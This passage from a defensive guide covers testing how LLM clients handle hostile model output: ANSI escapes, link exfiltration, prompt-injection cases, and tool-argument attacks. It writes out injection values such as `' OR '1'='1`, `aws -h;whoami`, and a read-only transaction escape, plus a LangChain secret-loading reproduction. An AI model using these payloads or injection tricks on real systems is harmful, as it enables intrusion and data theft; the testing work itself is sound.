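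Phishing is the stronger finding in Permiso's post, because a user has little reason to doubt an account warning that appears inside ChatGPT's answer. The post doesn't show script running or private conversation text leaving ChatGPT. The company's first report to OpenAI mentioned XSS in its title, but its revised report did not. The image addresses were fixed in advance, so they carried no data from the conversation.

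Permiso reported the problem to OpenAI on 29 April, and OpenAI marked the report "Not Reproducible" the next day for lack of detail. Permiso sent a fuller version on 1 May, which OpenAI first classed as not applicable and later as a duplicate of an earlier report. Permiso asked for clarification on 7 May, and its timeline lists no reply before publication. eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* found no sign of a fix at the end of May.

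The attack combines prompt injection with a display problem, and a stub can test the display problem. The tester has the stub return a reply with an external link and image, then checks whether the client loads the image and whether the user can see where the link leads. Permiso wants assistants to separate web content from their own output more clearly. That would help with quoted passages, but a model mixes its sources as it writes, so the client often has no way to identify which words came from the page.

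### Restricting addresses

OpenAI gives two reasons why a list of trusted websites isn't enough to stop these leaks. Many respectable sites have redirects, so a link can start on a trusted domain and end on an attacker's server. A strict list also produces so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

OpenAI instead checks whether the exact address was already public. Its crawler collects addresses from the open web and has no access to anyone's conversations. If the crawler has seen an address, ChatGPT may load it automatically, because the address is unlikely to contain that user's private data. Otherwise ChatGPT tries another site or warns the user before loading the address. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* adds that the warning shows the user what information would be sent.

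An attacker can still leak data through a choice among public addresses. Embrace The Red gives the example of a website with 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit. Hidden instructions tell the model to spell out a secret by visiting the matching pages in order. A choice among n addresses reveals at most log₂ n bits, which is about 5 bits per visit for 36 pages and 12 for 4,096. Rehberger suggests forbidding repeat visits to the same address within a session, which makes the attack harder but still lets some information out.

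Other companies' address checks have also had gaps. In *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, Willison had admired the restrictions on the tool Claude uses to fetch web pages, but in 2026 he reported that Ayush Paul had found a hole in them.

OpenAI also says that its check does not make a page trustworthy or prevent social engineering. The check therefore offers little protection against ChatGPhish's fake notices.

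The shop can be much stricter than ChatGPT because its assistant needs little of the web. It could remove every image address from the reply and have the model output a product number, which the client would use to build the address of the product photo. A CSP that permits images only from the shop's own server would enforce this in the browser, including after redirects. Links need a separate rule because a CSP does not generally control where a click leads. The client could keep links to the shop's own pages and show all others as plain text. Testers should still look for a page on the shop's site that redirects visitors to any address in its parameters.

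### Chat platforms: previews, mentions and commands

A chat platform's automatic link previews (unfurling) can leak data even if the client never loads a link. Embrace The Red recorded preview requests from Discord, Skype, Slack, Telegram, Signal and Microsoft Teams in 2023, and Discord's current documentation describes how it reads pages for previews. The request often comes from the platform's servers, where the shop's CSP and firewall have no effect.

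*Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, by the AI security company PromptArmor, applies this to OpenClaw, an agent people can talk to through messaging apps. With the default Telegram settings, an injected instruction could make OpenClaw reply with a link containing private data, and Telegram would fetch the link as soon as the message arrived. Setting `linkPreview: false` in OpenClaw's configuration fixes this. PromptArmor also runs a public page that records preview requests, so users can check their own combination of agent and app. Testers should send it only made-up data, or use their own server.

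Slack does the same. According to Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, it previews links in messages from apps by default, and a client can prevent this by setting both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false. These settings apply to one message at a time, so if the shop later adds a second notifier, its developer has to set them again. Slack's default behaviour also applies if a support worker copies the link into another channel, because the new message comes from a person.

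The shop's notifier needs a test for each of three effects:

| Text in the reply | Sign of a bug |
|---|---|
| `https://canary.example/a17` | The test server receives a preview request |
| `@everyone canary-a17` | Every test account receives a notification |
| `!canary-a17` | A test bot runs the command of that name |

The tester should run these tests in a private channel that contains only test accounts, because a failed mention test would otherwise disturb the whole staff. The mention must also use the platform's own syntax, such as `@everyone` on Discord.

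Mass mentions can also be on by default. *Source code for discord.mentions*, part of a Python library for Discord bots, shows that a bot's messages may notify everyone unless the developer changes the `AllowedMentions` setting. Changing it once for the whole client is safer than changing it for each message. DiscordPHP's *AllowedMentions*, the documentation for a similar PHP library, adds that Discord also checks the bot's permissions. The shop can therefore deny the bot permission to notify everyone, which protects the channel even if a developer forgets the setting.

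Bot commands are a problem when another bot reads the same channel and acts on messages that start with an exclamation mark. Embrace The Red recommends commands that a user has to start explicitly, such as Discord's slash commands. Bots can also ignore messages from other bots. If the shop doesn't control the other bot, its notifier can start each post with fixed words such as "Ticket summary:", so that the model never writes the first character. This doesn't stop a bot that searches the whole message for commands.

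### How terminals act on control characters

A terminal receives text and formatting instructions in a single stream. Most instructions start with the escape character (code 27, or `1b` in hexadecimal). Following it with `[31m` turns the text red, and following it with `[0m` returns the text to normal. Programs use these ANSI escape sequences for coloured error messages and progress bars. If a client prints a reply unchanged, the terminal processes any escape sequences in the reply just as it processes the client's own.

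This requires the model to produce the escape character, and in November 2024 Leon Derczynski reported that many models can. Within two weeks, Rehberger published *Terminal DiLLMa* on Embrace The Red. He found that prompting a model to write control characters worked but sometimes took several tries. Having the model run a short program that printed them was more reliable. He later discovered that models can also read control characters, so an attacker can place them in a document and ask the model to repeat them.

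Rehberger wrote a small command-line tool that sent a file or web page to GPT-4o and printed the reply. He then hid instructions in the pages it summarised. His test cases included these effects:

- **Hidden or altered text.** The reply could make text invisible, delete earlier words with backspaces, or move the cursor and clear the screen.
- **Clipboard writes.** The reply could place text on the user's clipboard. Most terminals he tried removed the final line break, but some kept it, so pasting the text could immediately run it as a command.
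- **Hyperlinks.** The terminal in the code editor VS Code displayed clickable links whose addresses contained data from the conversation. It asked for confirmation before opening them. Apple's Terminal did not support such links.
- **DNS requests.** Apple's Terminal could be made to look up a domain name without a click. The name itself can contain private data, which then reaches whoever runs the domain's name server.
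- **Flooding.** The reply could repeat one character a great many times to make the terminal unusable.

The results depended heavily on the terminal, so the shop should test the programs that its support workers actually use. Two harmless markers cover the basics. They appear here as a stub would write them in JSON, where `\u001b` stands for the escape character and `\r` for a carriage return:

```json
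"\u001b[31mcanary-a17\u001b[0m"
"hidden\rcanary"
```

If the first marker appears in red, the terminal has interpreted the escape sequence in the reply. The second marker tests the carriage return, a control character that needs no escape sequence. It moves the cursor to the start of the line, so an unprotected terminal overwrites "hidden" with "canary".

### Trail of Bits' test of Claude Code

In 2025 the security firm Trail of Bits found the same weakness in Claude Code. Its *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* reports that version 0.2.76 did not filter escape sequences from the descriptions and outputs of outside tools. These tools connect through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for giving models access to other software. The hostile text came from a tool rather than from the model, but it reached the same sink.

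The attack relied on the difference between what the user saw and what the model read. In one demonstration, a tool returned notes about the user's computers that included a sentence, in white text on a white background, requiring Python downloads to come from a particular server. The user could not see the sentence, but the model followed it and recommended the attacker's server. The researchers also showed how to overwrite an instruction with a fake security report, clear the screen, or display one web address while linking to another.

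The white text would have been plainly visible on a dark background, which many developers use. The other techniques do not depend on colour.

Neither Trail of Bits nor Anthropic appears to have published a retest, so the finding applies to version 0.2.76 and may not hold for Claude Code today. In April 2026, MITRE added specific advice on LLM output to *CWE-150*, an entry in a standard catalogue of software weaknesses, after a suggestion from Erick Galinkin of NVIDIA.

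### Making control characters harmless

Trail of Bits suggests replacing every `1b` byte with a placeholder, reasoning that all escape sequences in modern terminals start with it. This is easy to implement and works even when streaming splits a sequence across two pieces. But it misses backspaces, carriage returns and U+009B, a single character that some terminals accept in place of the escape character and bracket.

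Embrace The Red recommends caret notation, which replaces each control character with a visible pair of characters, such as `^[` for escape and `^H` for backspace. The Unix command `cat -v` does the same for files. Rehberger argues that caret notation should be the default for LLM output, with an option to turn it off.

MITRE advises clients to allow only printable characters and the kinds of whitespace they need, and rates this as highly effective. It gives a lower rating to removing escape codes from the model's vocabulary, since a model might still assemble them from several tokens. Whitespace can still cause harm in the shop's staff terminal tool, where a line break in a summary can create a fake ticket and a carriage return can overwrite a real one. The tool should encode both, and can add its own colours and line breaks afterwards.

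Deleting control characters from displayed text can mislead the user if the client uses the original text elsewhere. MITRE lists a program that removed escape sequences from a file name when it asked for permission to open the file, but kept them in the name it then used. The user could approve one file and give access to another. Caret notation is safer in such a dialog because it shows the user that the name contains control characters.

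### One reply, several encodings

No single cleaning step suits every sink. If the shop escapes a ticket summary for HTML when the reply arrives, support workers will see `&lt;` instead of `<` in their terminals, and the terminals will still act on any escape sequences in the text. It is better to store the reply unchanged and encode it for each sink just before use.

| In the reply | Web chat page | Staff terminal tool | Chat notifier |
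|---|---|---|---|
| `<b>` | Escape or sanitize | Print as text | Send as text |
| Escape character | Remove | Print as `^[` | Remove |
| Outside web address | Show as plain text | Print as text | Turn off previews |
| `@everyone` | Show as text | Print as text | Turn off mass mentions |
| Line break | Keep | Print as `^J` | Keep |

Stored raw replies remain dangerous to any new program that reads them. Logs are easy to overlook. If the shop's client writes raw replies to a log file, a developer who opens it with `cat` will trigger the escape sequences that the staff terminal tool had made harmless.

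## Output that is executed or parsed: tool calls, queries and data objects

The shop's fourth sink, the database lookup tool `find_order`, displays nothing, so a hostile reply can do damage there before anyone reads it. Developers often protect tool calls with a schema, which lists the fields the arguments must contain and the type of each. A value with the right shape can still be harmful when the database, shell or file system interprets its content.

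### Valid JSON, harmful value

Suppose the schema for `find_order` requires one field, `order_id`, containing a string. All four of these arguments pass:

| Argument | What could happen |
|---|---|
| `{"order_id": "1182"}` | The client looks up the customer's order |
| `{"order_id": "1183"}` | The client looks up someone else's order |
| `{"order_id": "1182' OR '1'='1"}` | If the client pastes the value into its SQL, the query returns every order |
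| `{"order_id": "../canary-a17"}` | If the client uses the value in a file name, the file ends up outside the intended folder |

A stricter schema could require exactly four digits. It would reject the last two values but still accept 1183, because a schema cannot check whose order that is.

*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) describes a public case of this flaw, in which a shopping chatbot passed any order number to its lookup function without checking who was asking. The numbers had a fixed prefix and six digits, so an outsider could try one after another and collect other customers' e-mail addresses and shipping details. The paper concludes that the model usually just carries hostile input to an existing, ordinary web vulnerability. The ordinary fix also works here. The shop's client should take the customer's identity from the login session,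 never from the model's reply, and check it on every lookup.

The same researchers built TicketOracle, a deliberately vulnerable concert site, to study tools that accept a web address. Its assistant has one tool, which fetches whatever address the model supplies. An attacker can ask the assistant for the site's administration pages, which accept connections only from the server itself. The tool runs on that server, so the pages accept its requests. The attack's success rate varied substantially among seven models, although all of them used the same tool. A safer tool would accept an event number and build the address itself.

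### From a city name to running code

In May 2026 Microsoft described two vulnerabilities its researchers had found in Semantic Kernel, its open-source framework for building agents. In both, a valid tool argument reached a dangerous sink.

The first, CVE-2026-26030, affected the Python version. The researchers demonstrated it with an agent that finds hotels:

1. The user asks for hotels in Paris, and the model calls `search_hotels` with the argument `city="Paris"`.
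2. The framework inserts the city into the text of a small Python function, `lambda x: x.city == 'Paris'`, which picks out the matching hotels.
3. The framework passes that text to `eval()`, which runs it as code.

If the city contains a quotation mark, the name ends early and Python treats the rest as code. A harmless test value is `' or True or '`, which produces this function:

```python
lambda x: x.city == '' or True or ''
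```

The function now matches every hotel. With a longer value, the researchers started the Windows calculator on the machine running the agent.

Semantic Kernel's developers had anticipated this kind of attack. Their validator accepted only a single lambda function and rejected it if it contained any name on a list of dangerous names. The code then ran without Python's built-in functions, such as `open`. The researchers' payload passed the validator because it was inside a lambda and used names missing from the list. It then reached the operating system through Python's class hierarchy, without using the built-in functions.

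The patch, in version 1.39.4, relies mainly on allowlists. It permits only simple syntax, such as comparisons, boolean logic and arithmetic, and only approved function calls. The code may use only one name, the function's own parameter `x`. The patch still uses a blocklist for attributes that lead into the class hierarchy.

These four layers should stop a city name from running commands. But `or` and `True` are permitted syntax, so a stray quotation mark might still change which records come back unless the framework also escapes the value. That would hardly matter for a list of hotels, but it would be a leak in an application that uses the filter to keep customers' records apart. Testers should send the harmless value to a patched client too, and count the records it returns.

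An agent was vulnerable only if it used the Search Plugin with the In-Memory Vector Store in its default configuration and an attacker could influence the agent's input. Microsoft adds that upgrading doesn't reveal whether someone exploited the flaw earlier. Owners should check whether the agent's process started any unexpected programs before the upgrade.

### The file tool that developers exposed by accident

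The second flaw, CVE-2026-25592, was in the .NET version. Semantic Kernel has a plugin that lets an agent run Python in a sandbox in Microsoft's cloud. The sandbox is isolated and has its own file system, and helper functions on the agent's machine copy files in and out of it.

One helper, `DownloadFileAsync`, carried the label `[KernelFunction]` by mistake. The label adds a function to the list of tools that the client offers the model. The model could therefore choose the helper's `localFilePath` argument, and the framework wrote the downloaded file to that path without checking it. An attacker needed two tool calls:

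1. The first created a script inside the sandbox, where it could do no harm to the agent's machine.
2. The second copied the script to the Windows Startup folder on that machine. Windows would run it the next time the user signed in.

Each call was well formed, since a path to the Startup folder is a valid string. The upload helper had the reverse problem in both the Python and .NET versions. It accepted any local path, so an attacker could have the agent copy private keys into the sandbox.

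Version 1.71.0 removes the label, so the framework no longer offers the download function to the model. Developers can still call the function from their own code, and the patch adds a check for that case. The check resolves the path to remove tricks such as `..` and compares the result with a list of permitted folders. Uploads received a similar check, but developers have to turn it on.

A tester can check for this kind of mistake by comparing the list of tools in the client's request to the stub with the list the developers intended. The stub can also return a call to a function that isn't on the client's list. A client that looks up names among all its functions, not just those it offered, would run that function.

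### When the model writes the query

`find_order` accepts only one value from the model. Many other clients let the model write the whole database query, which gives an attacker much more to exploit.

Pedro, Carreira and colleagues (2023) were the first to study the problem, in *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*. They built a job site with a chatbot based on LangChain, a framework for connecting models to other software. The model turned each question into SQL, LangChain ran it, and the model put the result into words. The chatbot's database account could read and change everything in the database.

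With LangChain's standard prompt, the chatbot ran whatever a visitor requested. It deleted the table of users on command, and it changed a person's phone number when someone asked in plain English. The researchers then added rules to the prompt forbidding changes to data and reading other people's records, but they bypassed both rules in all 30 attempts. They also planted an instruction in a job posting that made the chatbot tell other visitors there were no jobs. This attack worked every time when the chatbot could run one query per question, and 60% of the time when it could run several.

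Those rates come from GPT-3.5 and a 2023 version of LangChain, so they are poor evidence of how easily current models can be manipulated. The design fault doesn't depend on the model. The only limit was an instruction in the prompt, and the account itself had unrestricted permissions.

In their follow-up, *Words Become SQL*, Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues (2025) found the same fault when they attacked five open-source applications that used GPT-3.5 or GPT-4. Nearly every attack succeeded, and the main exceptions were attacks blocked by ordinary code. One application ran exactly one query per question, so text planted in the database could not trigger a second, and at least one application blocked all writes. Attacks on GPT-4 usually took more careful prompting than attacks on GPT-3.5, but the researchers did not count that as a defence because a determined attacker still got through.

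### Read-only tools that could write

Some developers have since moved the limit out of the prompt and into a database tool meant to be read-only. That is a better place for it, but several of these tools have proved easy to bypass.

Anthropic's reference server for connecting models to PostgreSQL databases wrapped each query in a read-only transaction, inside which the database refuses any change. Datadog Security Labs' *MCP vulnerability case study* (2025) explains how to leave the transaction. The server accepted several statements in one string, so the model's "query" could end the transaction itself. A test on a scratch database might look like this:

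```sql
BEGIN TRANSACTION READ ONLY;               -- from the tool
COMMIT; CREATE TABLE canary_a17 (id int);  -- from the reply
ROLLBACK;                                  -- from the tool
```

`COMMIT` closes the read-only transaction, the database creates the table, and the tool's `ROLLBACK` comes too late to undo it. Anthropic fixed the code in its repository in May 2025 and archived the project, but did not release the fix as a package. That August, developers were still downloading the vulnerable package about 21,000 times a week.

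Datadog recommends a database account with few rights but found this only a partial fix here. The server reused its connections, and even a restricted user could set a connection's time limit to one millisecond, which would make other people's queries on that connection fail. Datadog's patch sends each query as a prepared statement, which cannot contain a second statement, and then closes the connection.

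Other tools tried to detect dangerous SQL by checking its text. ProxySQL, a program that sits between applications and their databases, had a read-only tool that checked the query's first word, searched the text for forbidden words, and then sent the whole string over a connection that accepted several statements at once. According to OSV's *CVE-2026-48774*, an entry in a database of open-source vulnerabilities, a harmless `SELECT` followed by a command to rename a table would pass these checks. Sawicki, who reported the flaw, notes that each design choice behind it was understandable on its own.

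Even a single statement can get around a word list. NVD's *CVE-2025-67509* concerns Neuron, a PHP framework for agents. The framework's query tool required queries to start with a word such as `SELECT` and rejected a list of other words, but MySQL has a form of `SELECT` that writes its results to a file. Akamai, a network security company, found a different gap in a tool for the Apache Doris database. The tool put the database name argument in front of the query without validating it, and its SQL check read only the beginning of the text. A tester who put hostile SQL only in the `query` argument could have missed this, so tests need hostile values for every argument.

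In September 2026, AWS announced two such flaws in its own PostgreSQL tool. In *CVE-2026-85787* (2026), the list of forbidden SQL was incomplete, so a query could change data in read-only mode. In the more serious *CVE-2026-87911* (2026), the tool allowed PostgreSQL's `COPY ... TO PROGRAM`, which passes data to an operating system command. This worked only on databases that customers ran themselves, and only if the tool's account was a superuser or had the specific right to start programs. Version 1.1.7 fixes both flaws. AWS still calls a dedicated account with minimal rights the strongest control, because the database then enforces the limit whatever SQL it receives.

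### Shells and templates

Command shells, like databases, are vulnerable because one string can contain more than one instruction. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian discuss CVE-2025-5277, a flaw in a tool through which models could run AWS's command-line program. In the input `aws -h;whoami`, the first command prints the program's help text. The shell treats the semicolon as the end of that command and then runs `whoami`, which prints the current user's name.

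Such tools often run on a developer's own computer, where an outsider can't reach them directly, but the security firm Snyk showed that an attacker can reach them through the developer's coding assistant. In Snyk's example, a file in a code repository instructed the assistant to add `;whoami` to every call and not mention it. The developer could then make a harmless request, such as listing storage folders, and the assistant would send `whoami` along with the requested command.

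A client can avoid this by starting the program without a shell and passing the arguments as a list. The semicolon then has no special meaning. The client should still check for arguments that begin with a hyphen, because the program may treat them as options.

Template engines, which fill in documents such as e-mails, have this weakness as well because they evaluate expressions between double braces. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite an agent that used the model's reply as a template for Jinja2, a Python template engine, so an attacker could run operating system commands. Testers can send `{{7*7}}` and look for 49 in the result. Keeping the template constant and passing the reply in as a value prevents the injection, because Jinja2 inserts values without evaluating them.

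### Data that comes back as an object

Data that a client only stores can still be dangerous when the client reads it again. Serialization turns a program's objects into text, and deserialization rebuilds them. LangChain marks its serialized objects with a reserved key, `lc`. GitHub's *GHSA-C67J-W6G6-Q2CM* (2025), the advisory for CVE-2025-68664, explains that LangChain did not escape ordinary data containing this key, so it treated that data as one of its own objects when deserializing it.

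The error takes only a few lines to reproduce. Here the test environment contains a variable named `CANARY_A17` with the value `fake-secret`:

```python
from langchain_core.load import dumps, loads

data = {"note": {"lc": 1, "type": "secret", "id": ["CANARY_A17"]}}
text = dumps(data)
result = loads(text)
# Vulnerable versions: result["note"] is "fake-secret"
```

The input was a dictionary with three entries. `loads` treated it as a reference to a secret, looked up the environment variable and put its value in the result. Many applications keep their API keys in such variables. To steal a key, an attacker would also need the application to display the restored data or send it somewhere. Other `lc` structures could create certain LangChain objects with arguments the attacker chose, and some of those objects contact the network or access files as soon as they are created.

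According to GitHub, the most common route was through metadata. LangChain keeps some parts of a reply in the fields `additional_kwargs` and `response_metadata`, which an attacker can influence through prompt injection. A developer who looked only at the reply's text would not have noticed the injected data. Developers who never called `dumps` could still be vulnerable, because LangChain serialized data internally in two older streaming functions, in its handling of message history and in some caches.

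OSV's *CVE-2025-68664* (2025) gives the flaw a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 and lists versions 0.3.81 and 1.2.5 as fixed. The patch escapes the `lc` key in ordinary data and also makes loading stricter by default:

- `allowed_objects` is set to `"core"`, so `load` and `loads` rebuild only approved classes from LangChain's core package.
- `secrets_from_env` is now `False`. LangChain no longer reads secrets from the environment unless the developer turns this on.
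- A new setting, `init_validator`, blocks Jinja2 templates, which can run code.

The last two settings still matter after the escaping fix because an application may load text that `dumps` did not write, such as a file from another user. Developers can loosen all three, so testers should check both the client's version and how it calls these functions. LangChain's JavaScript version had the same escaping bug, recorded in NVD's *CVE-2025-68665*, and needed its own patch.

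### A stream that contained commands

Streamed replies usually arrive as server-sent events, and each event can have a type that tells the client what to do with it. Open WebUI, a popular chat interface that organisations run on their own servers, had an event type called `execute`. Simonovich (2026), in *Vulnerability Discovered in Open WebUI Enables Account Takeover and Remote Code Execution*, describes how a model server could misuse it. In simplified form, a harmless test event looks like this:

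```json
{"type": "execute", "data": {"code": "document.title='canary-a17'"}}
```

Open WebUI's page took the text in `code`, turned it into a JavaScript function with `new Function()` and ran it. That code could read the token that kept the user logged in, because Open WebUI stored it in `localStorage`, browser storage open to any script on the same site. With the token, an attacker could take over the account and read the user's chats and documents.

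An attacker could exploit this flaw, CVE-2025-64496, only if an administrator had turned on Direct Connections, which lets users add their own model servers. NVD's *CVE-2025-64496* notes that this feature is off by default. A user also had to add the attacker's server and send it a message. To run code on the Open WebUI server as well, the attacker needed a victim with the `workspace.tools` permission, which lets a user create tools in Python. These conditions help explain why the severity score is 7.3 out of 10, which is high but not critical. But people do try free model servers that colleagues or online communities recommend, so the conditions are less unusual than they look.

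Simonovich reported the flaw on 8 October 2025, and a first patch eleven days later was incomplete. The databases disagree about the last vulnerable version, but both NVD and GitLab's *CVE-2025-64496* (2025) list 0.6.35 as fixed. That version blocks `execute` events from direct connections. The filter depends on where an event comes from, so a tester should try the same event over every other route into the page.

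A stub that returned only the standard events of a chat completion API would not have exposed the flaw. Testers have to read the client's code and list every event type it handles to find the unusual ones.

### Choosing a fix

The right fix depends on how much of the instruction comes from the reply. If the reply supplies only a value, the client can keep the instruction fixed. In a parameterized query, the program sends the SQL and the values separately, so the database never interprets a value as SQL:

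```python
db.execute(
    "SELECT status FROM orders WHERE id = %s AND customer_id = %s",
    (order_id, session.customer_id),
)
```

The value `1182' OR '1'='1` now matches no order, because the database looks for an order with that whole string as its name. The second condition handles order 1183 by taking the customer's number from the session, so nothing in the reply can change it.

Parameterized queries don't help much when the model writes the entire query, because all of the SQL is then untrusted. Datadog acknowledges that agents often need such open-ended tools. The client then has to limit what any query can do:

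| What the reply supplies | How to limit it | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| A whole SQL query | Minimal database account, one statement per call, time limit | The query reads anything the account can read |
| A command | List of permitted programs and options, no shell | A permitted command deletes the wrong thing |
| A file path | Resolve the path, then compare it with permitted folders | The client overwrites a file in a permitted folder |
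| Program code | Sandbox without credentials or network access | The code uses whatever the sandbox can reach |
| A serialized object | Plain data, or a short list of permitted classes | A permitted class has side effects |

For the first row, Pedro and colleagues also suggest rewriting queries. If customer 5 asks for an e-mail address and the model writes a query for everyone's, the client replaces the table of users with a smaller one that contains only customer 5. The rewriting code has to find every table that the query mentions, including in nested queries, so it needs careful testing too. PostgreSQL's row-level security can apply a similar rule inside the database, but AWS warns that superusers bypass it.

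*Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a survey of systems that turn questions into queries, also recommends read-only execution and checking each query before it runs. It adds that agents which process results with Python must run that code in a sandbox. Semantic Kernel already did this, and the sandbox was not breached, but the helper function outside it could write anywhere on the agent's machine. Testers should therefore examine every function that moves data into or out of a sandbox.

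Allowlists have a better record than blocklists. Semantic Kernel's old validator, Neuron's tool and AWS's tool all failed because someone had to anticipate every dangerous word. An omission from an allowlist usually breaks a legitimate request, and a user will complain about it. Where a client calls `eval`, `exec` or `new Function()` on text from a reply, the safest change is nearly always to remove the call. A filter such as `x.city == 'Paris'` needs only an ordinary comparison in the client's own code.

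### Whether a grammar can remove the problem

Some developers want to stop dangerous output before the model produces it. In *Prompt Fuzzing is Pointless*, ctrlaidel argues for grammar-constrained decoding and calls it complete prevention. A grammar can make some output impossible, and ctrlaidel is right that instructions in a prompt only make bad output less likely.

A model writes one token at a time, choosing from a list of probabilities. Let L be the set of all strings that the grammar allows, w the output so far and t a possible next token. The server keeps t only if w followed by t could still grow into a string in L:

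p′(t | w) ∝ p(t | w) if wt is the beginning of some string in L, and p′(t | w) = 0 otherwise.

If the model finishes, its output is always in L. If it reaches the token limit first, the client receives only the beginning of a string in L. The method doesn't control which string in L the model produces.

The post's example is a calculator tool. The client asks the model for an arithmetic expression and passes the answer to `eval()`. In a demonstration by Garrett Galloway, a malicious test server returns a Python command that creates a file instead of `2+2`, and the client runs it. The post's grammar allows only numbers, spaces, parentheses and the operators `+`, `-`, `*` and `/`. That blocks the attack, since a Python command of this kind needs letters and quotation marks. Other expressions get through:

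| Expression | Does the grammar allow it? | Result if the client evaluates it |
|---|---|---|
| `2+2` | Yes | 4 |
| `open('canary-a17.txt', 'w')` | No | Python would create a file |
| `1/0` | Yes | An error, which stops a client that doesn't catch it |
| `9**9**9` | Only if two operators may stand side by side | Python tries to compute a number with about 370 million digits |
| `2-2`, when the user asked for 2+2 | Yes | A wrong answer |

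A better grammar would exclude the fourth expression by requiring a number between operators. The client could also limit the expression's length and evaluation time. But arithmetic is an unusually easy case, because almost no sum is harmful. Most tools accept values that are harmful only in context. A grammar for the shop's order numbers would allow 1183 as well as 1182. An SQL grammar that permits only `SELECT` would still let a query read every customer's address, and a grammar for file paths would have accepted the Startup folder unless it listed the permitted folders. The shop's chat page needs free text, and no grammar could distinguish a true delivery date from a false one.

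The other limitation is that the model server applies the grammar, and the client receives only the result. A hostile server can ignore the grammar, and a router can replace the reply after an honest server has applied it. Requesting constrained output would not have protected the calculator in Galloway's demonstration, because his server has no model and applies no constraint.

The post partly recognises this. It claims that constrained decoding saves the work of checking output afterwards, but also tells developers to compare the expression with the grammar before evaluating it. Only that comparison stops the demonstrated attack. The client should parse the expression with its own copy of the grammar, reject anything that doesn't fit, and calculate the result from the parsed numbers and operators without calling `eval()`.

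Constrained decoding still improves reliability, since it reduces the number of malformed replies the client has to reject. It can also hide a missing check, because a client that has only received well-formed replies appears to work. A stub doesn't have to follow the grammar, so a tester can have it send the calculator a word where a number belongs and see whether the client rejects it.

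## Building the stub

A model's reply passes through several layers of software before it reaches a sink. The provider's server sends it over the network. A vendor library, such as OpenAI's Python package, turns the bytes into objects, and many clients add an agent framework such as LangChain on top. A tester can replace the model with a stub at any of these layers, but the test exercises only the code between the stub and the sink.

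### Three places to cut

| Where the tester cuts | Client code that still runs | Cost | Bugs it hides |
|---|---|---|---|
| A fake model object inside the program | The client's own code and part of the framework | A few lines per test, in the client's own language | Faults in parsing, joining streamed pieces, retries and timeouts |
| A local HTTP server that speaks the provider's format | Everything, including the vendor library | The tester has to imitate the format and keep it current | Faults that appear only with real replies the tester did not think to imitate |
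| A proxy that edits real replies | Everything, with the provider's own formatting | Token fees, a real key and network access | Faults in situations that the real model rarely produces |

A fake object is the quickest stub to write, but it gives the client a reply that is already parsed. In LangChain's *Unit testing* guide, the fake model `GenericFakeChatModel` takes a tool call's arguments as a Python dictionary. OpenAI's API sends them as a string, so a tester who can supply only a dictionary cannot test how the client handles a string that breaks off after `{"order_id": "11`. The JavaScript version, `fakeModel`, also ignores the schema for structured answers and returns whatever value the tester configured. LangChain explains that this keeps tests focused on application logic rather than parsing. That is reasonable for ordinary unit tests, but it skips a check that a hostile reply would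 have to pass, so the tester may also report bugs that the real library would have prevented.

A local server avoids both problems because the client communicates with it exactly as it does with the provider. The server can be written in any programming language, and the tester doesn't need to change the client's code.

The proxy is the most realistic of the three, but its tests are the hardest to repeat. *Chaos testing*, part of the documentation for the open-source mock server MockServer, describes placing the server in front of a real service and adding errors or delays to the replies it relays. A seed, a starting number for the random choices, makes the faults repeatable, but it can't make the model repeat its text, so the tester has to save every reply.

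Most of the shop's tests should use a local stub server. Fake objects are useful for checking a single sink after each code change, and a proxy can record real replies to compare with the stub's. Testers also use editing proxies by hand in the final penetration test.

### A minimal server

The server below answers the shop's chat completion requests. `REPLIES` is a list that the tester prepared, containing texts and tool calls.

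```text
on POST /v1/chat/completions:
    request = parse the JSON body
    turn    = count the messages whose role is "assistant"
    choice  = Random(SEED, turn).pick(REPLIES)

    if choice is a tool call:
        message = { role: "assistant", content: null,
                    tool_calls: [{ id: "call_" + turn,
                                   type: "function",
                                   function: { name: choice.name,

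arguments: choice.arguments }}]}
        reason  = "tool_calls"
    else:
        message = { role: "assistant", content: choice.text }
        reason  = "stop"

    reply = { id: "chatcmpl-" + SEED + "-" + turn,
              object: "chat.completion", created: now, model: request.model,
              choices: [{ index: 0, message: message,
                          finish_reason: choice.reason or reason }],
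              usage: choice.usage or ordinary values }

    write SEED, turn, request and reply to the log
    send reply
```

The server copies `choice.arguments` as a raw string without checking it, so the tester can send broken JSON. The tester can also use `choice.reason` and `choice.usage` to override the ordinary metadata.

The server chooses each reply by the seed and the turn, not by how many requests it has answered, so a client that retries a failed request gets the same reply. To reproduce a failure, the developer restarts the server with the same seed and the same version of `REPLIES`. The server writes the log entry before it sends the reply, because a hostile reply may crash the client or break the connection. The server should leave the API key out of the log even though the key is fake, since someone may later use the same server with a real one.

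Counting assistant messages works because a chat completion client normally sends the whole conversation with every request. OpenAI's Responses interface can store the conversation on the server instead, according to Strands Agents' *OpenAI Responses API*. A stub for that interface has to store each conversation too, because the next request may contain only the newest message.

Tests that run in parallel need another key to keep their conversations separate. MockServer's *LLM response mocking* takes this key from a header, a cookie or a URL parameter. It can also choose a reply based on what the conversation contains, such as a result from a named tool. The shop's tester could use this to return an ordinary `find_order` call first and a hostile summary only after the order details arrive.

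### Replies in pieces

When the client asks for streaming, the server sends a series of events, each starting with `data:` and ending with a blank line. Shortened, a streamed tool call looks like this:

```text
data: {"choices":[{"index":0,"delta":{"tool_calls":[{"index":0,"id":"call_1","type":"function","function":{"name":"find_order","arguments":""}}]}}]}

data: {"choices":[{"index":0,"delta":{"tool_calls":[{"index":0,"function":{"arguments":"{\"order"}}]}}]}

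data: {"choices":[{"index":0,"delta":{"tool_calls":[{"index":0,"function":{"arguments":"_id\": \"1182\"}"}}]}}]}

data: {"choices":[{"index":0,"delta":{},"finish_reason":"tool_calls"}]}

data: [DONE]
```

Only the first piece of a streamed tool call has the call's identifier and function name. The client uses `index` to match later pieces to the right call, then joins the argument strings in order. The small Python test server *openai mock server* ends its text streams the same way, with a `finish_reason` and then the `[DONE]` line.

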